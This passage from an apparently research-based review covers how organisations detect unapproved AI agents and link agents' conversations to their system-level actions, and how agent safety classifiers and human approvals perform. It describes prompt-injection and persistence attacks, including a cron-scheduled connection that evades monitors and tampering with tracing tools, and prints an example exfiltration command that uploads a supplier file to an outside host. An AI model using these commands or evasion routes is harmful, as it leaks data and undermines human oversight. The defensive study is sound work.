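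The evidence for call classifiers is more limited. MCPShield stopped every attack in the Adaptive Attack collection, but that collection has only ten servers, and Zhou and colleagues list robustness against adaptive attackers as future work. In Liu's follow-up, a language model rewrote each failed attack for a second attempt, but no agent attempted an attacker's goal in any of the 209 conclusive cases, so the experiment tested the agents' resistance and not the controllers'. Attacks can also fail to transfer to new tasks, as in Liu's first study, where one type of attack that had worked on the development tasks never succeeded on the test tasks.

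Permission lists should hold up better than text detectors. Liu's controllers don't use the attacker's text as input, so rewording it can't change their decision on a given call. An attacker would instead have to find a harmful action that the list permits, such as sending a secret to an approved address.

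## Experiments on finding agents that bypass the gateway

To find agents that bypass its gateway, an organisation has to look on employees' devices or in the network traffic those devices produce. In *Detecting Shadow AI*, Canale and Soulis (2026) tested the first approach with Agent Detector, an open-source program they wrote for Windows. Other researchers have tried to recognise AI traffic without decrypting it.

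### What an agent leaves on a device

Agent Detector runs once an hour and reads information that Windows already keeps. It doesn't read prompts or conversations, and it doesn't block anything. When it finds an unapproved agent, it shows the user a notice they have to acknowledge.

Canale and Soulis sort the evidence into six layers. On the same workstation, they compared Claude Code with a short Python script that imitates an agent.

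| Layer | Claude Code | Home-made Python agent |
|---|---|---|
| Software identity | `claude.exe`, recognised by its install path | None (Windows shows only `python.exe`) |
| Running processes | Had started command shells | Had started a command shell |
| Network | Connected to Anthropic's API | Connected to Anthropic's API |
| Installation | Editor extension, software package, launcher script | None |
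| Configuration | Folders in the user's profile | None |
| History | Recent change in its project-history folder | None |

Claude Code is easy to find because a catalogue can list its name, folders and publisher. Agent Detector's catalogue has 39 such tools. According to Canale and Soulis, Microsoft's Defender for Endpoint also discovers local agents from a list of named products. The home-made agent isn't a product, so these lists don't include it. Agent Detector also has a general rule for unlisted agents. It reports a probable agent when a process is connected to a model service and has a shell among its child or grandchild processes.

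To apply this rule, Agent Detector must identify the service at the other end of a connection. Windows lists the process and a numerical address for each connection, but not the service's name. Anthropic publishes a range of addresses used only for its API, so a connection to that range identifies the service. OpenAI and many others use content-delivery networks, whose addresses also serve unrelated websites. For these, Agent Detector checks the DNS cache, the machine's temporary record of recently looked-up names and their addresses. It rates such a match as low-confidence unless the process also runs a shell.

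### Agents and their behavioural twins

Suppose one script calls Anthropic's API every five seconds and runs a shell command after each call. A second script does the same but calls a public index of Python packages instead. The first looks like an agent, and the second is ordinary automation. Canale and Soulis call such a pair behavioural twins.

They describe each program by its behaviour and its identity. Behaviour covers which processes the program starts and the number, timing and volume of its connections. Identity covers the names of the software and of the services it contacts. Two programs are twins if they have the same behaviour but different identities. A detector that uses only behaviour receives the same input for both twins, so it gives both the same result. If one twin is an agent and the other is not, the detector either misses the agent or wrongly flags the other program.

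This is true by definition, so the practical question is how closely ordinary software resembles agents. Installing a package with the common tool `npm`, for example, opens encrypted connections and starts shells. But real agents may differ from real scripts in ways a better detector could use. Canale and Soulis mention that models stream their answers in small pieces and that agents may run a command just after an answer ends, but they did not test a detector that uses this timing.

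Identity alone isn't enough either, because a chat program also connects to a model service. The general rule therefore combines the two.

### Results on one workstation

Canale and Soulis ran 27 short test cases on one laptop. Each lasted about half a minute, during which Agent Detector scanned three times. They repeated the whole set five times with an ordinary user's rights and five times as administrator.

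- **Agents (12).** These were synthetic programs written in Python, Node.js or PowerShell. Most contacted a real model service with an invalid key, received an error, and sent harmless commands to a shell.
- **AI components (3).** These were an MCP server on its own, a program that loads software for running models, and a program that calls a model but has no tools.
- **Benign workloads (9).** Three were twins of the synthetic agents and five were developers' jobs, such as building software. The last was a script that had inherited a setting for a model service but didn't use it.
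- **Robustness cases (3).** These were agents that the researchers expected to be hard to find.

The experiments compared Agent Detector with three simple rules. The first looks for product names. The second flags interpreters, such as Python, that have an encrypted web connection and a shell, and the third flags any program that has both. In the table, a case counts as flagged if the detector flagged it in most of the five runs with an ordinary user's rights.

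| Detector | Agents found, of 12 | Benign workloads flagged, of 9 | AI components flagged, of 3 |
|---|---|---|---|
| Product names | 0 | 0 | 0 |
| Behaviour, interpreters only | 9 | 4 | 1 |
| Behaviour, any program | 10 | 4 | 1 |
| Agent Detector | 12 | 0 | 3 |

Both behavioural rules flagged all three twins and the `npm` installation. On the same laptop, the broader rule also flagged the code editor VS Code and the program that runs the Windows desktop.

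Agent Detector got a perfect score, but it found two of the agents in only three of the five runs. With administrator rights, it found 11 of the 12 agents and missed one, which had intermittent connections, in every run. For two of the 12, it reported only a connection to a model service, as it did for the program without tools. If only reports of a probable agent count, it found ten.

Canale and Soulis also corrected the program after seeing its results on these cases. One early version flagged the script with the inherited setting, and the next missed all four agents whose providers use shared networks. Those five cases show that the corrections work, but they are no longer an independent test. The corrected program raised no false alarms on the nine benign workloads, but with so few workloads, its actual false positive rate could still be as high as about 28%.

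Agent Detector missed all three robustness cases: an agent that reached its model through an unlisted intermediary, one that had finished running before the scan, and one inside a virtual machine. The behavioural rules caught the first, but they would also have flagged its harmless counterpart.

### How quickly the evidence disappears

In these tests, Agent Detector scanned within seconds of each agent's start, when the evidence was fresh. Two more experiments measured how much harder detection becomes later.

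The first experiment used an agent that called Anthropic's API every ten seconds, closed the connection five seconds after each call and ran a shell only briefly. Canale and Soulis scanned it 40 times at random intervals over about seven minutes. The agent had an open connection during 18 of the scans, and Agent Detector reported it in 15, or 38% (95% confidence interval 23% to 54%). Agent Detector found a connection and a shell at the same time in only four scans. If the provider had used a shared network, where a connection alone gives low confidence, about one scan in ten would have detected the agent.

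Hourly scans have more chances to find an agent that is used regularly. If this agent worked for three hours and each scan had an independent 37.5% chance of finding it, three scans would have about a 76% chance (1 − 0.625³) of finding it at least once. If each scan had a 10% chance, the combined chance would be about 27%.

In the second experiment, agents kept connections open to four providers on shared networks. Canale and Soulis scanned every 15 seconds for six minutes and repeated the test three times. All 12 agents stayed connected, but after 295 seconds Agent Detector could not identify the service behind any connection because the names had expired from the DNS cache. OpenAI's entries expired fastest. Agent Detector identified the OpenAI connection for 55 seconds in one repetition, ten seconds in another and not at all in the third.

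If an agent keeps one such connection open for an hour and no other program looks up the provider's name, a scan at a random moment has at most a 295 in 3,600 chance, or about 8%, of identifying the service. Agents that reconnect often are easier to identify, because each new connection usually refreshes the cache. When the researchers made the agents close their connections after each call, Agent Detector identified the service in 25 of the 31 scans that found an agent connected.

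Continuous recording would avoid much of this problem. Microsoft's Sysmon can log each new process, connection and name lookup, together with the process responsible. A rule could then flag any process that looks up a model service and later starts a shell, even if the process runs for only a few seconds. Canale and Soulis suggested this rule but did not test it. Continuous recording would also produce far more data than an hourly scan.

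Scanning hourly would use little processor time by comparison, less than ten seconds a day. The median scan took 154 milliseconds.

### From one workstation to a whole company

The synthetic agents received error messages instead of answers and did no real work. Most kept a connection and a shell available throughout, whereas a real agent may wait for its user or edit files without starting a shell. The experiment therefore can't show what share of real agents an hourly scan would find. Agent Detector reported the three AI tools active on the laptop (Claude Code, GitHub Copilot and OpenAI's Codex application), but it recognised them as products, which is the easier task.

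The rate of false alarms in a company is just as uncertain. If one scan in 1,000 wrongly triggered a notice, a company with 1,000 laptops, each scanned eight times a day, would interrupt eight people a day. A test of nine benign workloads on one laptop is too small to show whether the real rate would be higher or lower. Shared networks could cause false alarms. If a browser has recently looked up a model provider, another program that connects to an unrelated site at the same address may appear to be using the model. None of the benign workloads triggered this error, but few of them used shared networks.

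The laptop also ran a consumer edition of Windows outside any company's device-management system, and the tests only approximated the privileged account the program would normally use. Canale and Soulis propose a field study in which the program reports its findings for a few weeks without showing notices.

Even a correct finding shows only that a certain user's program appears to be an agent. It doesn't include the agent's tool calls, so an organisation can't use it to count the risky actions that bypassed the gateway. But it gives the organisation a program and a user to ask about. If all approved agents connect to the gateway's address, a direct connection from an agent to a model provider is itself evidence that the agent is bypassing the gateway.

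### Recognising encrypted traffic

*One task to rule them all* (2025) notes that domain names are still commonly unencrypted in TLS traffic, and that network operators usually use them to classify traffic. An operator can identify a model service this way unless the name is encrypted or belongs to an intermediary that isn't on the operator's list.

Researchers have therefore tested what the size, direction and timing of encrypted packets reveal. Many model services send an answer in pieces as the model generates it. Encryption hides the words but not the size of each piece or the delay before the next. *Whisper Leak* (2025) uses these patterns to infer the topic of a user's prompt.

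In *A Large-Scale Benchmark and Risk Assessment of Traffic Analysis Attacks*, Pouryousef, Lopez and colleagues (2026) recorded 60,000 exchanges with ten models and trained classifiers to tell the models apart. In *Exposing LLM User Privacy via Traffic Fingerprint Analysis*, Zhang, Deng and colleagues (2025) did the same for 50 agents, using the traffic between the agents and their users. In *ANT*, Li, Gao and colleagues (2026) recorded 3,114 sessions of agents running locally and tested 13 existing classifiers on them.

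| Experiment | What the classifier had to identify | Result |
|---|---|---|
| Pouryousef and colleagues | Which of ten models | 97.7% balanced accuracy (recall averaged over the models) |
| Pouryousef and colleagues | Which of six kinds of prompt, from the response traffic | 67.4% accuracy, against 16.7% by guessing |
| Zhang and colleagues | Which of 50 agents | F1 score of 0.866 (the harmonic mean of precision and recall) |
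| Li and colleagues | Which of five types of agent task | 43.1% to 72.7% accuracy, depending on the classifier |

None of these experiments measured how well a classifier could find an agent in ordinary office traffic. Pouryousef and colleagues assume that every recording comes from a known list of models, and that the observer knows where each exchange begins and ends. Zhang and colleagues also tested recordings from agents that were not among the 50, and the median F1 score stayed above 0.80, but that test separated known agents from unknown ones rather than agents from other sources of traffic, such as a software update. All the traffic that Li and colleagues recorded came from agents, and each session ran in its own isolated network.

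Accuracy also falls when conditions change. Rewording the prompts reduced Pouryousef and colleagues' accuracy in recognising models from 93.2% to 69.5%. In another test, they identified which of ten tasks a team of agents was working on. Accuracy was 83% when the agents coordinated as they had in the training data and 52% when they coordinated differently. A company would probably have to retrain such a classifier often, because providers and users keep changing models, prompts and agent programs.

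Li and colleagues also tested whether classifiers could detect harmful use from traffic. Their test set had 189 benign sessions and 20 malicious ones, in which agents attacked a practice website, wrote malicious code or tried to evade a sandbox. All 13 classifiers had an accuracy above 90%, but a program that never raised an alarm would also have scored 90.4%. Seven of the 13 missed more than half of the malicious sessions.

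One of the better classifiers, Deep Fingerprinting, caught 17 of the 20 malicious sessions and flagged 2 of the 189 benign ones. At those rates, a company with 10 malicious sessions among 10,000 would get about 8 or 9 true alarms and 106 false ones.

Results also depended on the kind of misuse. Four classifiers detected nearly all the attacks on the website but none of the sessions with malicious code or sandbox evasion. Scanning and attacking a website produces distinctive traffic, whereas writing malicious code produces much the same traffic as writing any other code.

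All these methods require a capture point, a place on the network path where the organisation can record packets. A recorder in the office misses traffic from laptops that connect from elsewhere. It also misses queries to a local model, as a model gateway does. Canale and Soulis add that traffic analysis doesn't identify the process or user responsible. An organisation could instead record packets on each laptop, as Li and colleagues did on the machines that ran their agents. But software installed on a laptop could also read directly from Windows which program opened each connection.

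## Experiments on linking an agent's words to its effects on the machine

Canale and Soulis's Agent Detector can report that an agent is running, but it doesn't record what the agent does. Other tools record the programs an agent starts, the files it opens and the connections it makes. To explain these events, an analyst also needs to know which part of the agent's conversation led to them.

### Two records of one action

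Suppose that the hijacked agent in the invoice example runs a script, `sh month_end.sh`, and the script uploads the supplier list. The application record (prompts, model replies and tool calls) may show only that short command and the output "done". The operating system's record could contain these lines (simplified):

```
execve   curl -T suppliers.csv https://collect.example/in
openat   /home/user/suppliers.csv
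connect  203.0.113.42, port 443
sendto   48210 bytes
```

Each line of the record is a system call, a program's request to the kernel, the core of the operating system. The lines show a program starting, opening the supplier list, connecting to an outside address and sending data. They don't show that the employee had asked for a summary of invoices, or that one invoice contained a hidden instruction. With only this record, an analyst couldn't tell the theft from a transfer the employee wanted.

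The gap also affects rules about agents' behaviour. *ActPlane* (Zheng, Wu and colleagues, 2026) gives the example of a rule that an agent must run the tests before it commits code. A check on tool calls misses a `git commit` inside a script that the agent wrote earlier. The researchers collected 1,361 rules for agents from the instruction files of 64 popular software projects. By their count, a program could enforce 45% of the rules using operating-system events, and would need to read the contents of files to enforce another 38%.

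### Matching by ancestry, time and arguments

*AgentSight* (Zheng, Yu and colleagues, 2025) describes a tool that records both an agent's words and its effects on a Linux machine, then matches the two records. It uses eBPF, a Linux feature that runs small programs inside the kernel when chosen events occur.

1. AgentSight attaches probes to the functions that the agent uses to encrypt and decrypt its traffic. The probes copy each prompt before encryption and each reply after decryption, so this step needs no gateway or root certificate.
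2. Other probes record when programs start, open files or make connections. A filter in the kernel keeps only events from the agent and its descendants, which are the processes it started, the processes those started, and so on.
3. AgentSight uses this family tree to connect an action with the agent. If the agent starts a shell and the shell starts `curl`, the tree connects `curl` with the agent.
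4. AgentSight links a model's reply to actions that follow within a window of 100 to 500 milliseconds.
5. It also looks for file names, web addresses and commands from the reply among the arguments of later system calls.
6. A second language model reads the matched events, judges whether they fit the agent's task and explains its verdict.

In the script example, the family tree would connect the upload with the agent. Finding the reply that caused the upload could be harder, because the reply mentions `month_end.sh` but not the supplier list, and the script might run for several seconds before it starts the upload.

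In one test, the researchers asked an agent to download and build a program. The agent followed the program's documentation to a web page with a hidden instruction, then sent the machine's list of user accounts to an outside server. AgentSight recorded 521 events and merged them into 37, and the second model identified an attack with high confidence. In two other tests, AgentSight revealed an agent that kept repeating a failing web search and a team of six agents that blocked one another by locking files.

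AgentSight slowed three programming tasks by 0.4% to 4.9%, with an average of 2.9% over three runs of each. The researchers didn't measure how often the second model flags harmless sessions. That model also reads text that an attacker may have written, a weakness it shares with other language models used as judges.

### Labels that travel with files

*AgentLoupe* (Bao, Liu and colleagues, 2026) describes an attack that evades this matching. A hijacked agent writes a script, schedules it with cron, the Linux service that runs programs at set times, and then exits. An hour later, cron runs the script, which opens a connection that lets the attacker control the machine. The agent didn't start cron, so the script isn't among the agent's descendants, and an hour is far longer than AgentSight's time window.

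AgentLoupe also captures the conversation by attaching probes to the encryption functions, but it gives each new, independent prompt a numbered label. It then passes the label on as follows:

- A process that a labelled process starts inherits the label.
- When a labelled process writes to a file, AgentLoupe attaches the label to the file.
- A process that later opens or runs the file takes over the label.
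- When a labelled process sends data through a network socket, AgentLoupe labels the socket, and the process that receives the data takes over the label.

In the cron attack, the agent's process labels the script and the schedule. When cron opens them, the label passes to cron and then to the shell that makes the connection. An analyst can follow the label back to the prompt.

Labels can also spread too far. If an agent edits a settings file that most programs read, its label could reach much of the machine. AgentLoupe limits this by starting a new label with each independent prompt and recording its link to the old one. It also stops older labels from replacing newer ones and blocks transfers between sessions, but records the rejected transfers. Users can make labels expire after a set time, although an attacker who waits longer would escape the trace.

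Bao and colleagues tested AgentLoupe on two attacks. In the cron attack, it recorded 165 log entries and linked the network connection to the exchange in which the model had produced the script. In the second attack, one session wrote a harmful instruction into `AGENTS.md`, a file of standing instructions for coding agents. A later session opened the file and, after an ordinary request from the user, ran a command that printed "hacked". AgentLoupe recorded 126 entries and linked the two sessions through the file. A language model read the linked events and reported both attacks, with stated confidence of 0.95 and 0.90.

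The researchers argue from AgentSight's design that it would miss both links, but they didn't run it on these attacks and leave a direct comparison for future work. They compared the two tools' effect on speed, averaging five runs per task.

| Task | AgentSight | AgentLoupe, labels not passed on | Full AgentLoupe |
|---|---|---|---|
| Reading a code repository | 4.5% slower | 1.7% slower | 4.5% slower |
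| Writing code | 2.5% slower | 3.1% slower | 8.0% slower |
| Compiling a program | 1.7% slower | 0.1% faster | 7.7% slower |

No monitoring tool should make compiling faster, so small differences in the table are probably noise. Passing on labels added the most overhead during compiling, which involves many system calls.

Bao and colleagues acknowledge that they haven't measured how often labels reach unrelated processes or fail to reach related ones. An analyst who follows a label therefore can't tell how likely the link is to be right.

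*Agent-Warden* (Cui, Gu and colleagues, 2026) tested a similar labelling tool in more runs, but on only one sequence of events. An agent's script wrote a file and renamed it, and an unrelated monitoring program later read it. The tool reconstructed the whole chain in all 120 runs, which covered two versions of the tool on two types of processor. Langfuse, an application tracer, recorded the agent's part but not the later reading. The researchers had prepared the sequence to match the tool's rules, so the perfect score is evidence that the software runs reliably, but not that it would make few labelling errors in ordinary work. Such errors are likely because the tool marks a parent process whenever a marked child exits, even if the parent never uses the child's output.

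Agent-Warden slowed the test workloads by 0.2% to 3.5%. It loses its file labels when the machine restarts, but a scheduled attack survives the restart. AgentLoupe also keeps its labels in memory and probably has the same problem.

### How the ACE corpus compares the two records

*On the Effectiveness of Kernel-Level Evidence for Agent Security* measures how much each kind of record helps a detector. Its detectors receive the evidence from a finished session and give the session a single score, whereas AgentSight and AgentLoupe match individual events with individual replies.

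The evidence comes from Agent Cross-Layer Evidence (ACE), a collection of 4,047 sessions. In each session, Claude Code, running on Claude Haiku 4.5, worked in a fresh container, an isolated environment for running programs. The standard Linux tool `strace` recorded 15 kinds of system call, about 3,500 events per session on average. The researchers also saved the agent's transcript and the lists of MCP tools.

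The sessions cover 17 threat models, including altered MCP servers, poisoned files and web pages, and harmful requests from the user. The researchers sorted the attacks into 12 mechanics according to what a sensor could observe, such as an injected shell command or a direct read of a credentials file.

Detectors used one of three views of each session.

| View | Numerical features | Examples |
|---|---|---|
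| Application | 29 | Length of the prompt, number of tool calls, wording of tool descriptions |
| Kernel | 57 | Number of programs started, number of different addresses contacted |
| Combined | 86 | All of the above |

Four of the ten detectors take the numerical features as input. AdaBoost and XGBoost use decision trees, and TabPFN and TabICL are pretrained models for tabular data. The other six are language models, whose input is the transcript and tool lists, a short summary of the system calls, or both. The researchers trained the three smaller language models on ACE sessions, and gave the three large Qwen models descriptions of attacks and 14 labelled examples.

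The labels depend partly on the same evidence that the detectors read. For most attacks, the researchers wrote a rule describing the attack's visible effect, such as opening a credentials file and then sending data to a certain address. They counted a session as malicious only if the rule matched. For 70 of the 141 attack designs, the rule used only system calls, which gives the kernel view an advantage. To check for this, they looked separately at 239 malicious sessions whose effect appeared at least partly in the application record. On unfamiliar attacks, the kernel view still did better than the application view for TabPFN, TabICL and the three smaller language models, so the labelling can't explain the whole difference.

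This left 1,358 malicious sessions and 2,293 that counted as harmless, including 1,002 in which the agent never used the tool under attack. The researchers excluded another 396 sessions in which the agent used the tool but the expected effect didn't appear. Counting those as malicious lowered AUROC by at most 0.045. When they also counted the 1,002 sessions as malicious, AUROC fell by 0.08 to 0.18.

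### Detection on unfamiliar attacks

The researchers first tested detectors on attack types that also appeared in the training data. All ten detectors did best with the combined view, with AUROCs from 0.831 to 0.994. In a second test, the researchers left one of seven attack families out of the training data and the Qwen models' examples, then tested the detectors on that family. The table gives the average over the seven families.

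| Detector | Application | Kernel | Combined |
|---|---|---|---|
| AdaBoost | 0.689 | 0.733 | 0.840 |
| XGBoost | 0.703 | 0.750 | 0.850 |
| TabPFN | 0.633 | 0.777 | 0.874 |
| TabICL | 0.636 | 0.764 | 0.801 |
| Qwen3-235B | 0.705 | 0.775 | 0.829 |
| Qwen3-80B | 0.678 | 0.725 | 0.810 |
| Qwen3-32B | 0.672 | 0.741 | 0.723 |
| Qwen2.5-3B, trained | 0.713 | 0.901 | 0.881 |
| Qwen2.5-7B, trained | 0.722 | 0.882 | 0.920 |
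| Llama-3.1-8B, trained | 0.688 | 0.922 | 0.791 |

Every detector did better with the kernel record than with the application record. Adding the application record to the kernel record improved seven of the ten scores, but the 95% confidence interval for the improvement excludes zero for only four detectors. Llama did clearly worse with both records than with the kernel record alone, which the researchers attribute to overfitting on the application text.

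The application view was at a disadvantage because 1,176 transcripts lacked the user's first prompt. But all six language models did better with the kernel view even on the sessions that included that prompt.

Llama's score of 0.922, the highest in the table, depends heavily on details of the laboratory setup. The summary of system calls lists the internet addresses that programs contacted and the temporary files they used. The staged attacks sent data to addresses reserved for documentation, which no real server uses. When the researchers replaced the external addresses and most of the temporary file names with placeholders and retrained the model, its AUROC fell to 0.759. Some drop is to be expected, because where data is sent is useful evidence in real attacks too. But real attackers wouldn't use such recognisable addresses. AdaBoost and XGBoost receive only counts, so their scores don't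 depend on particular addresses.

The form of the evidence also made a large difference. When given no attack descriptions or examples, the large Qwen models scored between 0.502 and 0.520 with the combined view, which is close to chance. Four other detectors read the system calls in their original order and scored between 0.517 and 0.578. A text classifier that read the short summary scored 0.836.

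### Attacks that one record misses

The researchers regard an AUROC of 0.75 as acceptable. For five of the 12 mechanics, the average AUROC across the ten detectors fell below this level in at least one of the two separate views. These results come from the easier test, in which the attack types also appear in the training data.

| Mechanic | Malicious sessions | Application | Kernel | Combined |
|---|---|---|---|---|
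| Silent theft through logging | 244 | 0.586 | 0.976 | 0.970 |
| Audit-log poisoning | 11 | 0.608 | 0.932 | 0.954 |
| Tampering with a tool's argument schema | 85 | 0.672 | 0.844 | 0.867 |
| Manipulation of the agent's preferences | 29 | 0.687 | 0.701 | 0.834 |
| Injection through a retrieved reference | 53 | 0.906 | 0.703 | 0.927 |

In silent theft, a tool reads credentials and copies them to a log while doing its ordinary job. Neither step appears in the transcript, but both require system calls. In injection through a retrieved reference, a planted document changes the agent's text, but the agent makes no unusual system calls.

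The two low kernel scores are close to the threshold. With a threshold of 0.70, the kernel view would pass on all 12 mechanics, while the application view would still fail on four. The result for audit-log poisoning is uncertain because it is based on only 11 malicious sessions.

Three kinds of attack in ACE leave no distinctive trace in either record: false content in a tool's result, signals in the timing between calls, and messages hidden in spaces and line breaks.

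### A different agent

The researchers also recorded 592 sessions with another agent, a small Python program running on Mistral's Devstral 2. These sessions covered five of the seven attack families with 13 attack designs. For each family, the researchers trained the detectors on ACE sessions with that kind of attack, or used such sessions as examples, so the test changes the agent but not the type of attack.

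XGBoost reached an average AUROC of 0.842, Llama 0.849 and Qwen3-80B 0.998, but TabPFN only 0.662. The researchers trace TabPFN's result to one feature, the number of different temporary files. Claude Code uses such files in every session, but the Python agent used none in 57% of its sessions. An update that changes how an agent stores temporary data could therefore make a detector less accurate even if the attacks stay the same.

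Averages hide large differences here too. Llama separated command injections perfectly from harmless sessions, but its AUROC for stolen credentials was only 0.605.

### Comparison with a scanner and a rule engine

The appendix of *On the Effectiveness of Kernel-Level Evidence for Agent Security* compares four of the detectors with Cisco's MCP scanner. The comparison uses 1,871 sessions, 731 of them malicious, from the part of ACE with altered MCP servers. The scanner used only its YARA text rules, which had found 21% of the poisoned descriptions in Mattsson and colleagues' experiment.

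| Detector | View | Recall | False positive rate |
|---|---|---|---|
| Cisco MCP Scanner | Tool descriptions and schemas | 15.9% | 16.3% |
| Qwen3-80B | Combined | 73.2% | 7.3% |
| TabPFN | Combined | 91.7% | 4.0% |
| XGBoost | Combined | 92.2% | 3.8% |
| Llama-3.1-8B | Kernel | 98.1% | 2.6% |

The scanner did no better than chance, for two main reasons. Its rules look for fixed phrases from published attacks, which the researchers had reworded. In addition, 52 of the 82 malicious server designs changed only the server's behaviour, not its tool list.

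The comparison is unfair to the scanner in some ways. The other detectors had seen the same types of attack in training or as examples, and Llama could still read the laboratory's addresses. A session also counts as harmless if the agent never used the poisoned tool, so a correct warning about that tool counts as a false alarm. Unlike the other detectors, the scanner can warn a company before the agent does any harm.

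If 10 of 10,000 sessions were malicious, even Llama would raise about 10 true alarms and 260 false ones. With a false positive rate of at most 1%, XGBoost would still find 86.2% of the attacks, but Qwen's recall would fall to 0.7%. Qwen gives many sessions the same confidence score, so no threshold separates them.

Every session in the corpus triggered at least one rule in Falco, an open-source program that applies rules to system calls. Recall and the false positive rate were therefore both 100%. The researchers used only the default rules that their recordings could support. Using the number of triggered rules as a score gave an AUROC of about 0.57. The rules suit servers, where a new shell or a hidden temporary file is unusual, but Claude Code produces both in ordinary work. A security team would normally adjust the rules to its own machines, but the researchers didn't test adjusted rules.

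### Containers and intact sensors

In ACE, each session had its own container and its own copy of `strace`, so every system call can be matched to the right session. The researchers checked this with 30 sessions, running three at a time, and found none of the 8,240 recorded events in the wrong log. An agent on an employee's laptop usually isn't separated from other programs in this way. The study excludes agents inside code editors and desktop applications, agents that were already running when recording began, and agents that share a machine without a container or similar wrapper. Without that separation, a monitoring tool would first have to work out which events belong to the agent, and its mistakes could lower the detection scores.

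The network was also artificial. A server in the laboratory accepted every outside connection, so stolen data always appeared to arrive. In a company, a firewall might block the connection, which would change the system calls.

The study also assumes that the sensor keeps working. The container gives programs permission to trace one another, which `strace` needs, but a malicious agent could use the same permission to interfere with `strace`. The recordings include the system call for such interference, but none of the ten detectors uses it. Cui and colleagues similarly assume for Agent-Warden that the attacker hasn't gained control of the kernel.

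## What measurements and surveys of deployed agents show

In an experiment, researchers choose an agent's tools, its tasks and the attacks it faces. Data from everyday use can show how common risky tools are, how people handle approval requests and how often alarms go off, but nobody knows in advance which of the recorded actions are harmful.

### Tools that change something

Stein's *How are AI agents used?* (2026) analysed 177,436 tools from 19,388 public MCP servers, created between November 2024 and February 2026. Stein searched GitHub and Smithery, a server directory, and found 73,338 candidates. Stein then removed duplicates and servers with no GitHub stars, and used Claude Sonnet 4.5 to discard entries that were only documentation or unrelated code.

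The same model then sorted the tools into three groups. Perception tools read data, reasoning tools analyse or plan, and action tools change something outside the agent, for example by editing a file, sending an email or transferring money. Fourteen people with postgraduate degrees each labelled 100 tools to check the sorting, and they agreed with the model on 81%.

Action tools make up 36% of the published tools, but their share of usage rose from 27% to 65% over the 16 months. Stein estimated usage from monthly downloads, which were available for 3,854 of the servers.

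The estimate treats each download of a server as one use of every tool on it, although a download records an installation rather than a tool call. If a file server has three tools that read files and seven that change them, an agent that installs it only to read files would still add seven action uses to the estimate. The data exclude remote servers, which need no download, and copies that a company keeps on its own network. They also exclude built-in tools, such as a coding agent's shell. Stein cautions that the downloads may mostly reflect what developers are trying out.

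The rise came mainly from general-purpose tools, such as those that control a web browser or a whole computer. These are harder to monitor than narrow tools. A call to a tool that transfers cryptocurrency has an obvious purpose, whereas a call to `browser_click` might open a news article or confirm a payment. Stein could track narrow payment tools fairly easily, and counted 47 servers that could make payments in January 2025 and 1,578 in February 2026. That count wouldn't include payments an agent makes through a browser.

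In *APEX-Harm* (2026), a laboratory benchmark set in simulated workplaces, an agent running Gemini 3.8 made 8,700 MCP calls over 180 runs. Of these, 7,625 (88%) went to a tool that executes code, and 66 went to the mail server. The agent used Python to search files and inspect spreadsheets, although it had separate tools for both. An MCP gateway that grouped these calls by tool name would put most of them under one heading, without distinguishing a file search from a spreadsheet inspection. The benchmark doesn't count the operations inside each script. All the runs contained attacks, so the shares in an ordinary office may differ.

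### Flaws in public servers

For *A First Look at the Security Issues in the Model Context Protocol*, Li and Gao (2025) collected 67,057 servers from six public registries. Their program, MCPInspect, checks a server's links, tool descriptions and code. They ran it on servers from the four registries that only link to code hosted elsewhere, and found 833 servers with exploitable vulnerabilities and 18 with suspicious descriptions. They didn't run it on servers from the other two registries, so dividing 833 by 67,057 would understate the share of checked servers it flagged as vulnerable.

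The number of servers an attacker could exploit depends on the program's precision. At 90% precision, about 750 of the 833 findings would be correct, and at 10% only about 83. Holzbauer and colleagues' check of flagged agent skills suggests that low precision is a realistic worry in such surveys. A count of findings also leaves out the vulnerable servers that a program misses.

Li and Gao found that configuration examples on the registry mcp.so can expose server owners' access tokens. An attacker could use such a token to insert malicious descriptions into a legitimate server without changing its registry listing.

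### Anthropic's classifier on its employees' calls

Agent developers have much better data on live use than outside researchers, and some publish part of it. Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* gives test results for that mode's classifier. Anthropic shows the classifier only the user's messages and the agent's tool calls, to protect it from persuasion by the agent and from hidden instructions.

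As in *SilentCall*, a quick first stage flags calls, and a slower second stage evaluates only those. Here both stages receive the same information, and the first is biased towards blocking. Anthropic tested them on three sets of actions.

| Test set | Error measured | First stage alone | Both stages |
|---|---|---|---|
| 10,000 real tool calls by Anthropic employees | Harmless calls blocked | 8.5% | 0.4% |
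| 52 real overeager actions | Harmful actions missed | 6.6% | 17% |
| 1,000 synthetic attempts to send data out | Harmful actions missed | 1.8% | 5.7% |

The second stage reduces blocked harmless calls from about 850 to 40 in 10,000, but it also makes the classifier miss more than twice as many overeager actions.

An employee had refused each of the 52 overeager actions, or a later review had flagged it. The classifier missed about nine of them. With so few cases, the true miss rate for such actions could be anywhere from about 9% to 30%. In most of the misses that Anthropic examined, the classifier had detected the danger but wrongly treated the action as approved by the user. For example, a user who writes "clean up the PR" (a pull request, or proposed code change) hasn't necessarily agreed to a force-push, which can overwrite earlier work.

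The false positive rate is harder to interpret. Anthropic doesn't explain how it established that the blocked calls among the 10,000 were harmless. It also doesn't say whether the 10,000 include calls that never reach the classifier, such as reading a file or editing one inside the project folder. If half of them never reach the classifier, the false positive rate among the calls it judged would be 0.8%.

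Results can vary widely with the cases tested. BestHub's *Can Claude Code's Auto Mode Replace Human Review?* summarises an outside stress test in which auto mode missed 81% of the actions that exceeded the agent's authority.

### How people handle approval requests

Before auto mode, Claude Code asked users to approve most commands and file changes. Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) reports that users approve 97% of these requests. A high approval rate is expected because most of the commands are probably safe. But users reject 39% of the plans Claude presents for approval, which suggests that they read plans more carefully than individual commands.

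Many users also avoid permission requests. A quarter of interactive sessions start in a mode that skips permission checks. As of June 2026, 49.5% of active command-line users had written a rule that lets the agent run certain shell commands without asking. Many of these rules allow any Python or Node.js program, which in practice allows almost anything.

These figures matter to organisations that count human approval as a safeguard, because a log entry marked "approved by user" may mean that the user considered the action carefully, approved it by reflex or wrote a rule months ago that allowed it. In sessions that skip permission checks, the user makes no approval decisions.

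Anthropic also directly tested whether people notice dangerous approval requests. A research vendor hired 1,053 testers for a coding study and, once in each session, replaced the text of an approval request with a clearly dangerous command. The testers refused 143 of the commands (13.6%), while auto mode blocked 937 of the same commands (89%). The testers' refusal rate fell from about 17% early in a session to about 5% after 50 or more requests. They may have taken less care than they would at work, because a mistake in the test environment couldn't damage anything of their own.

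### Serious harm in live sessions

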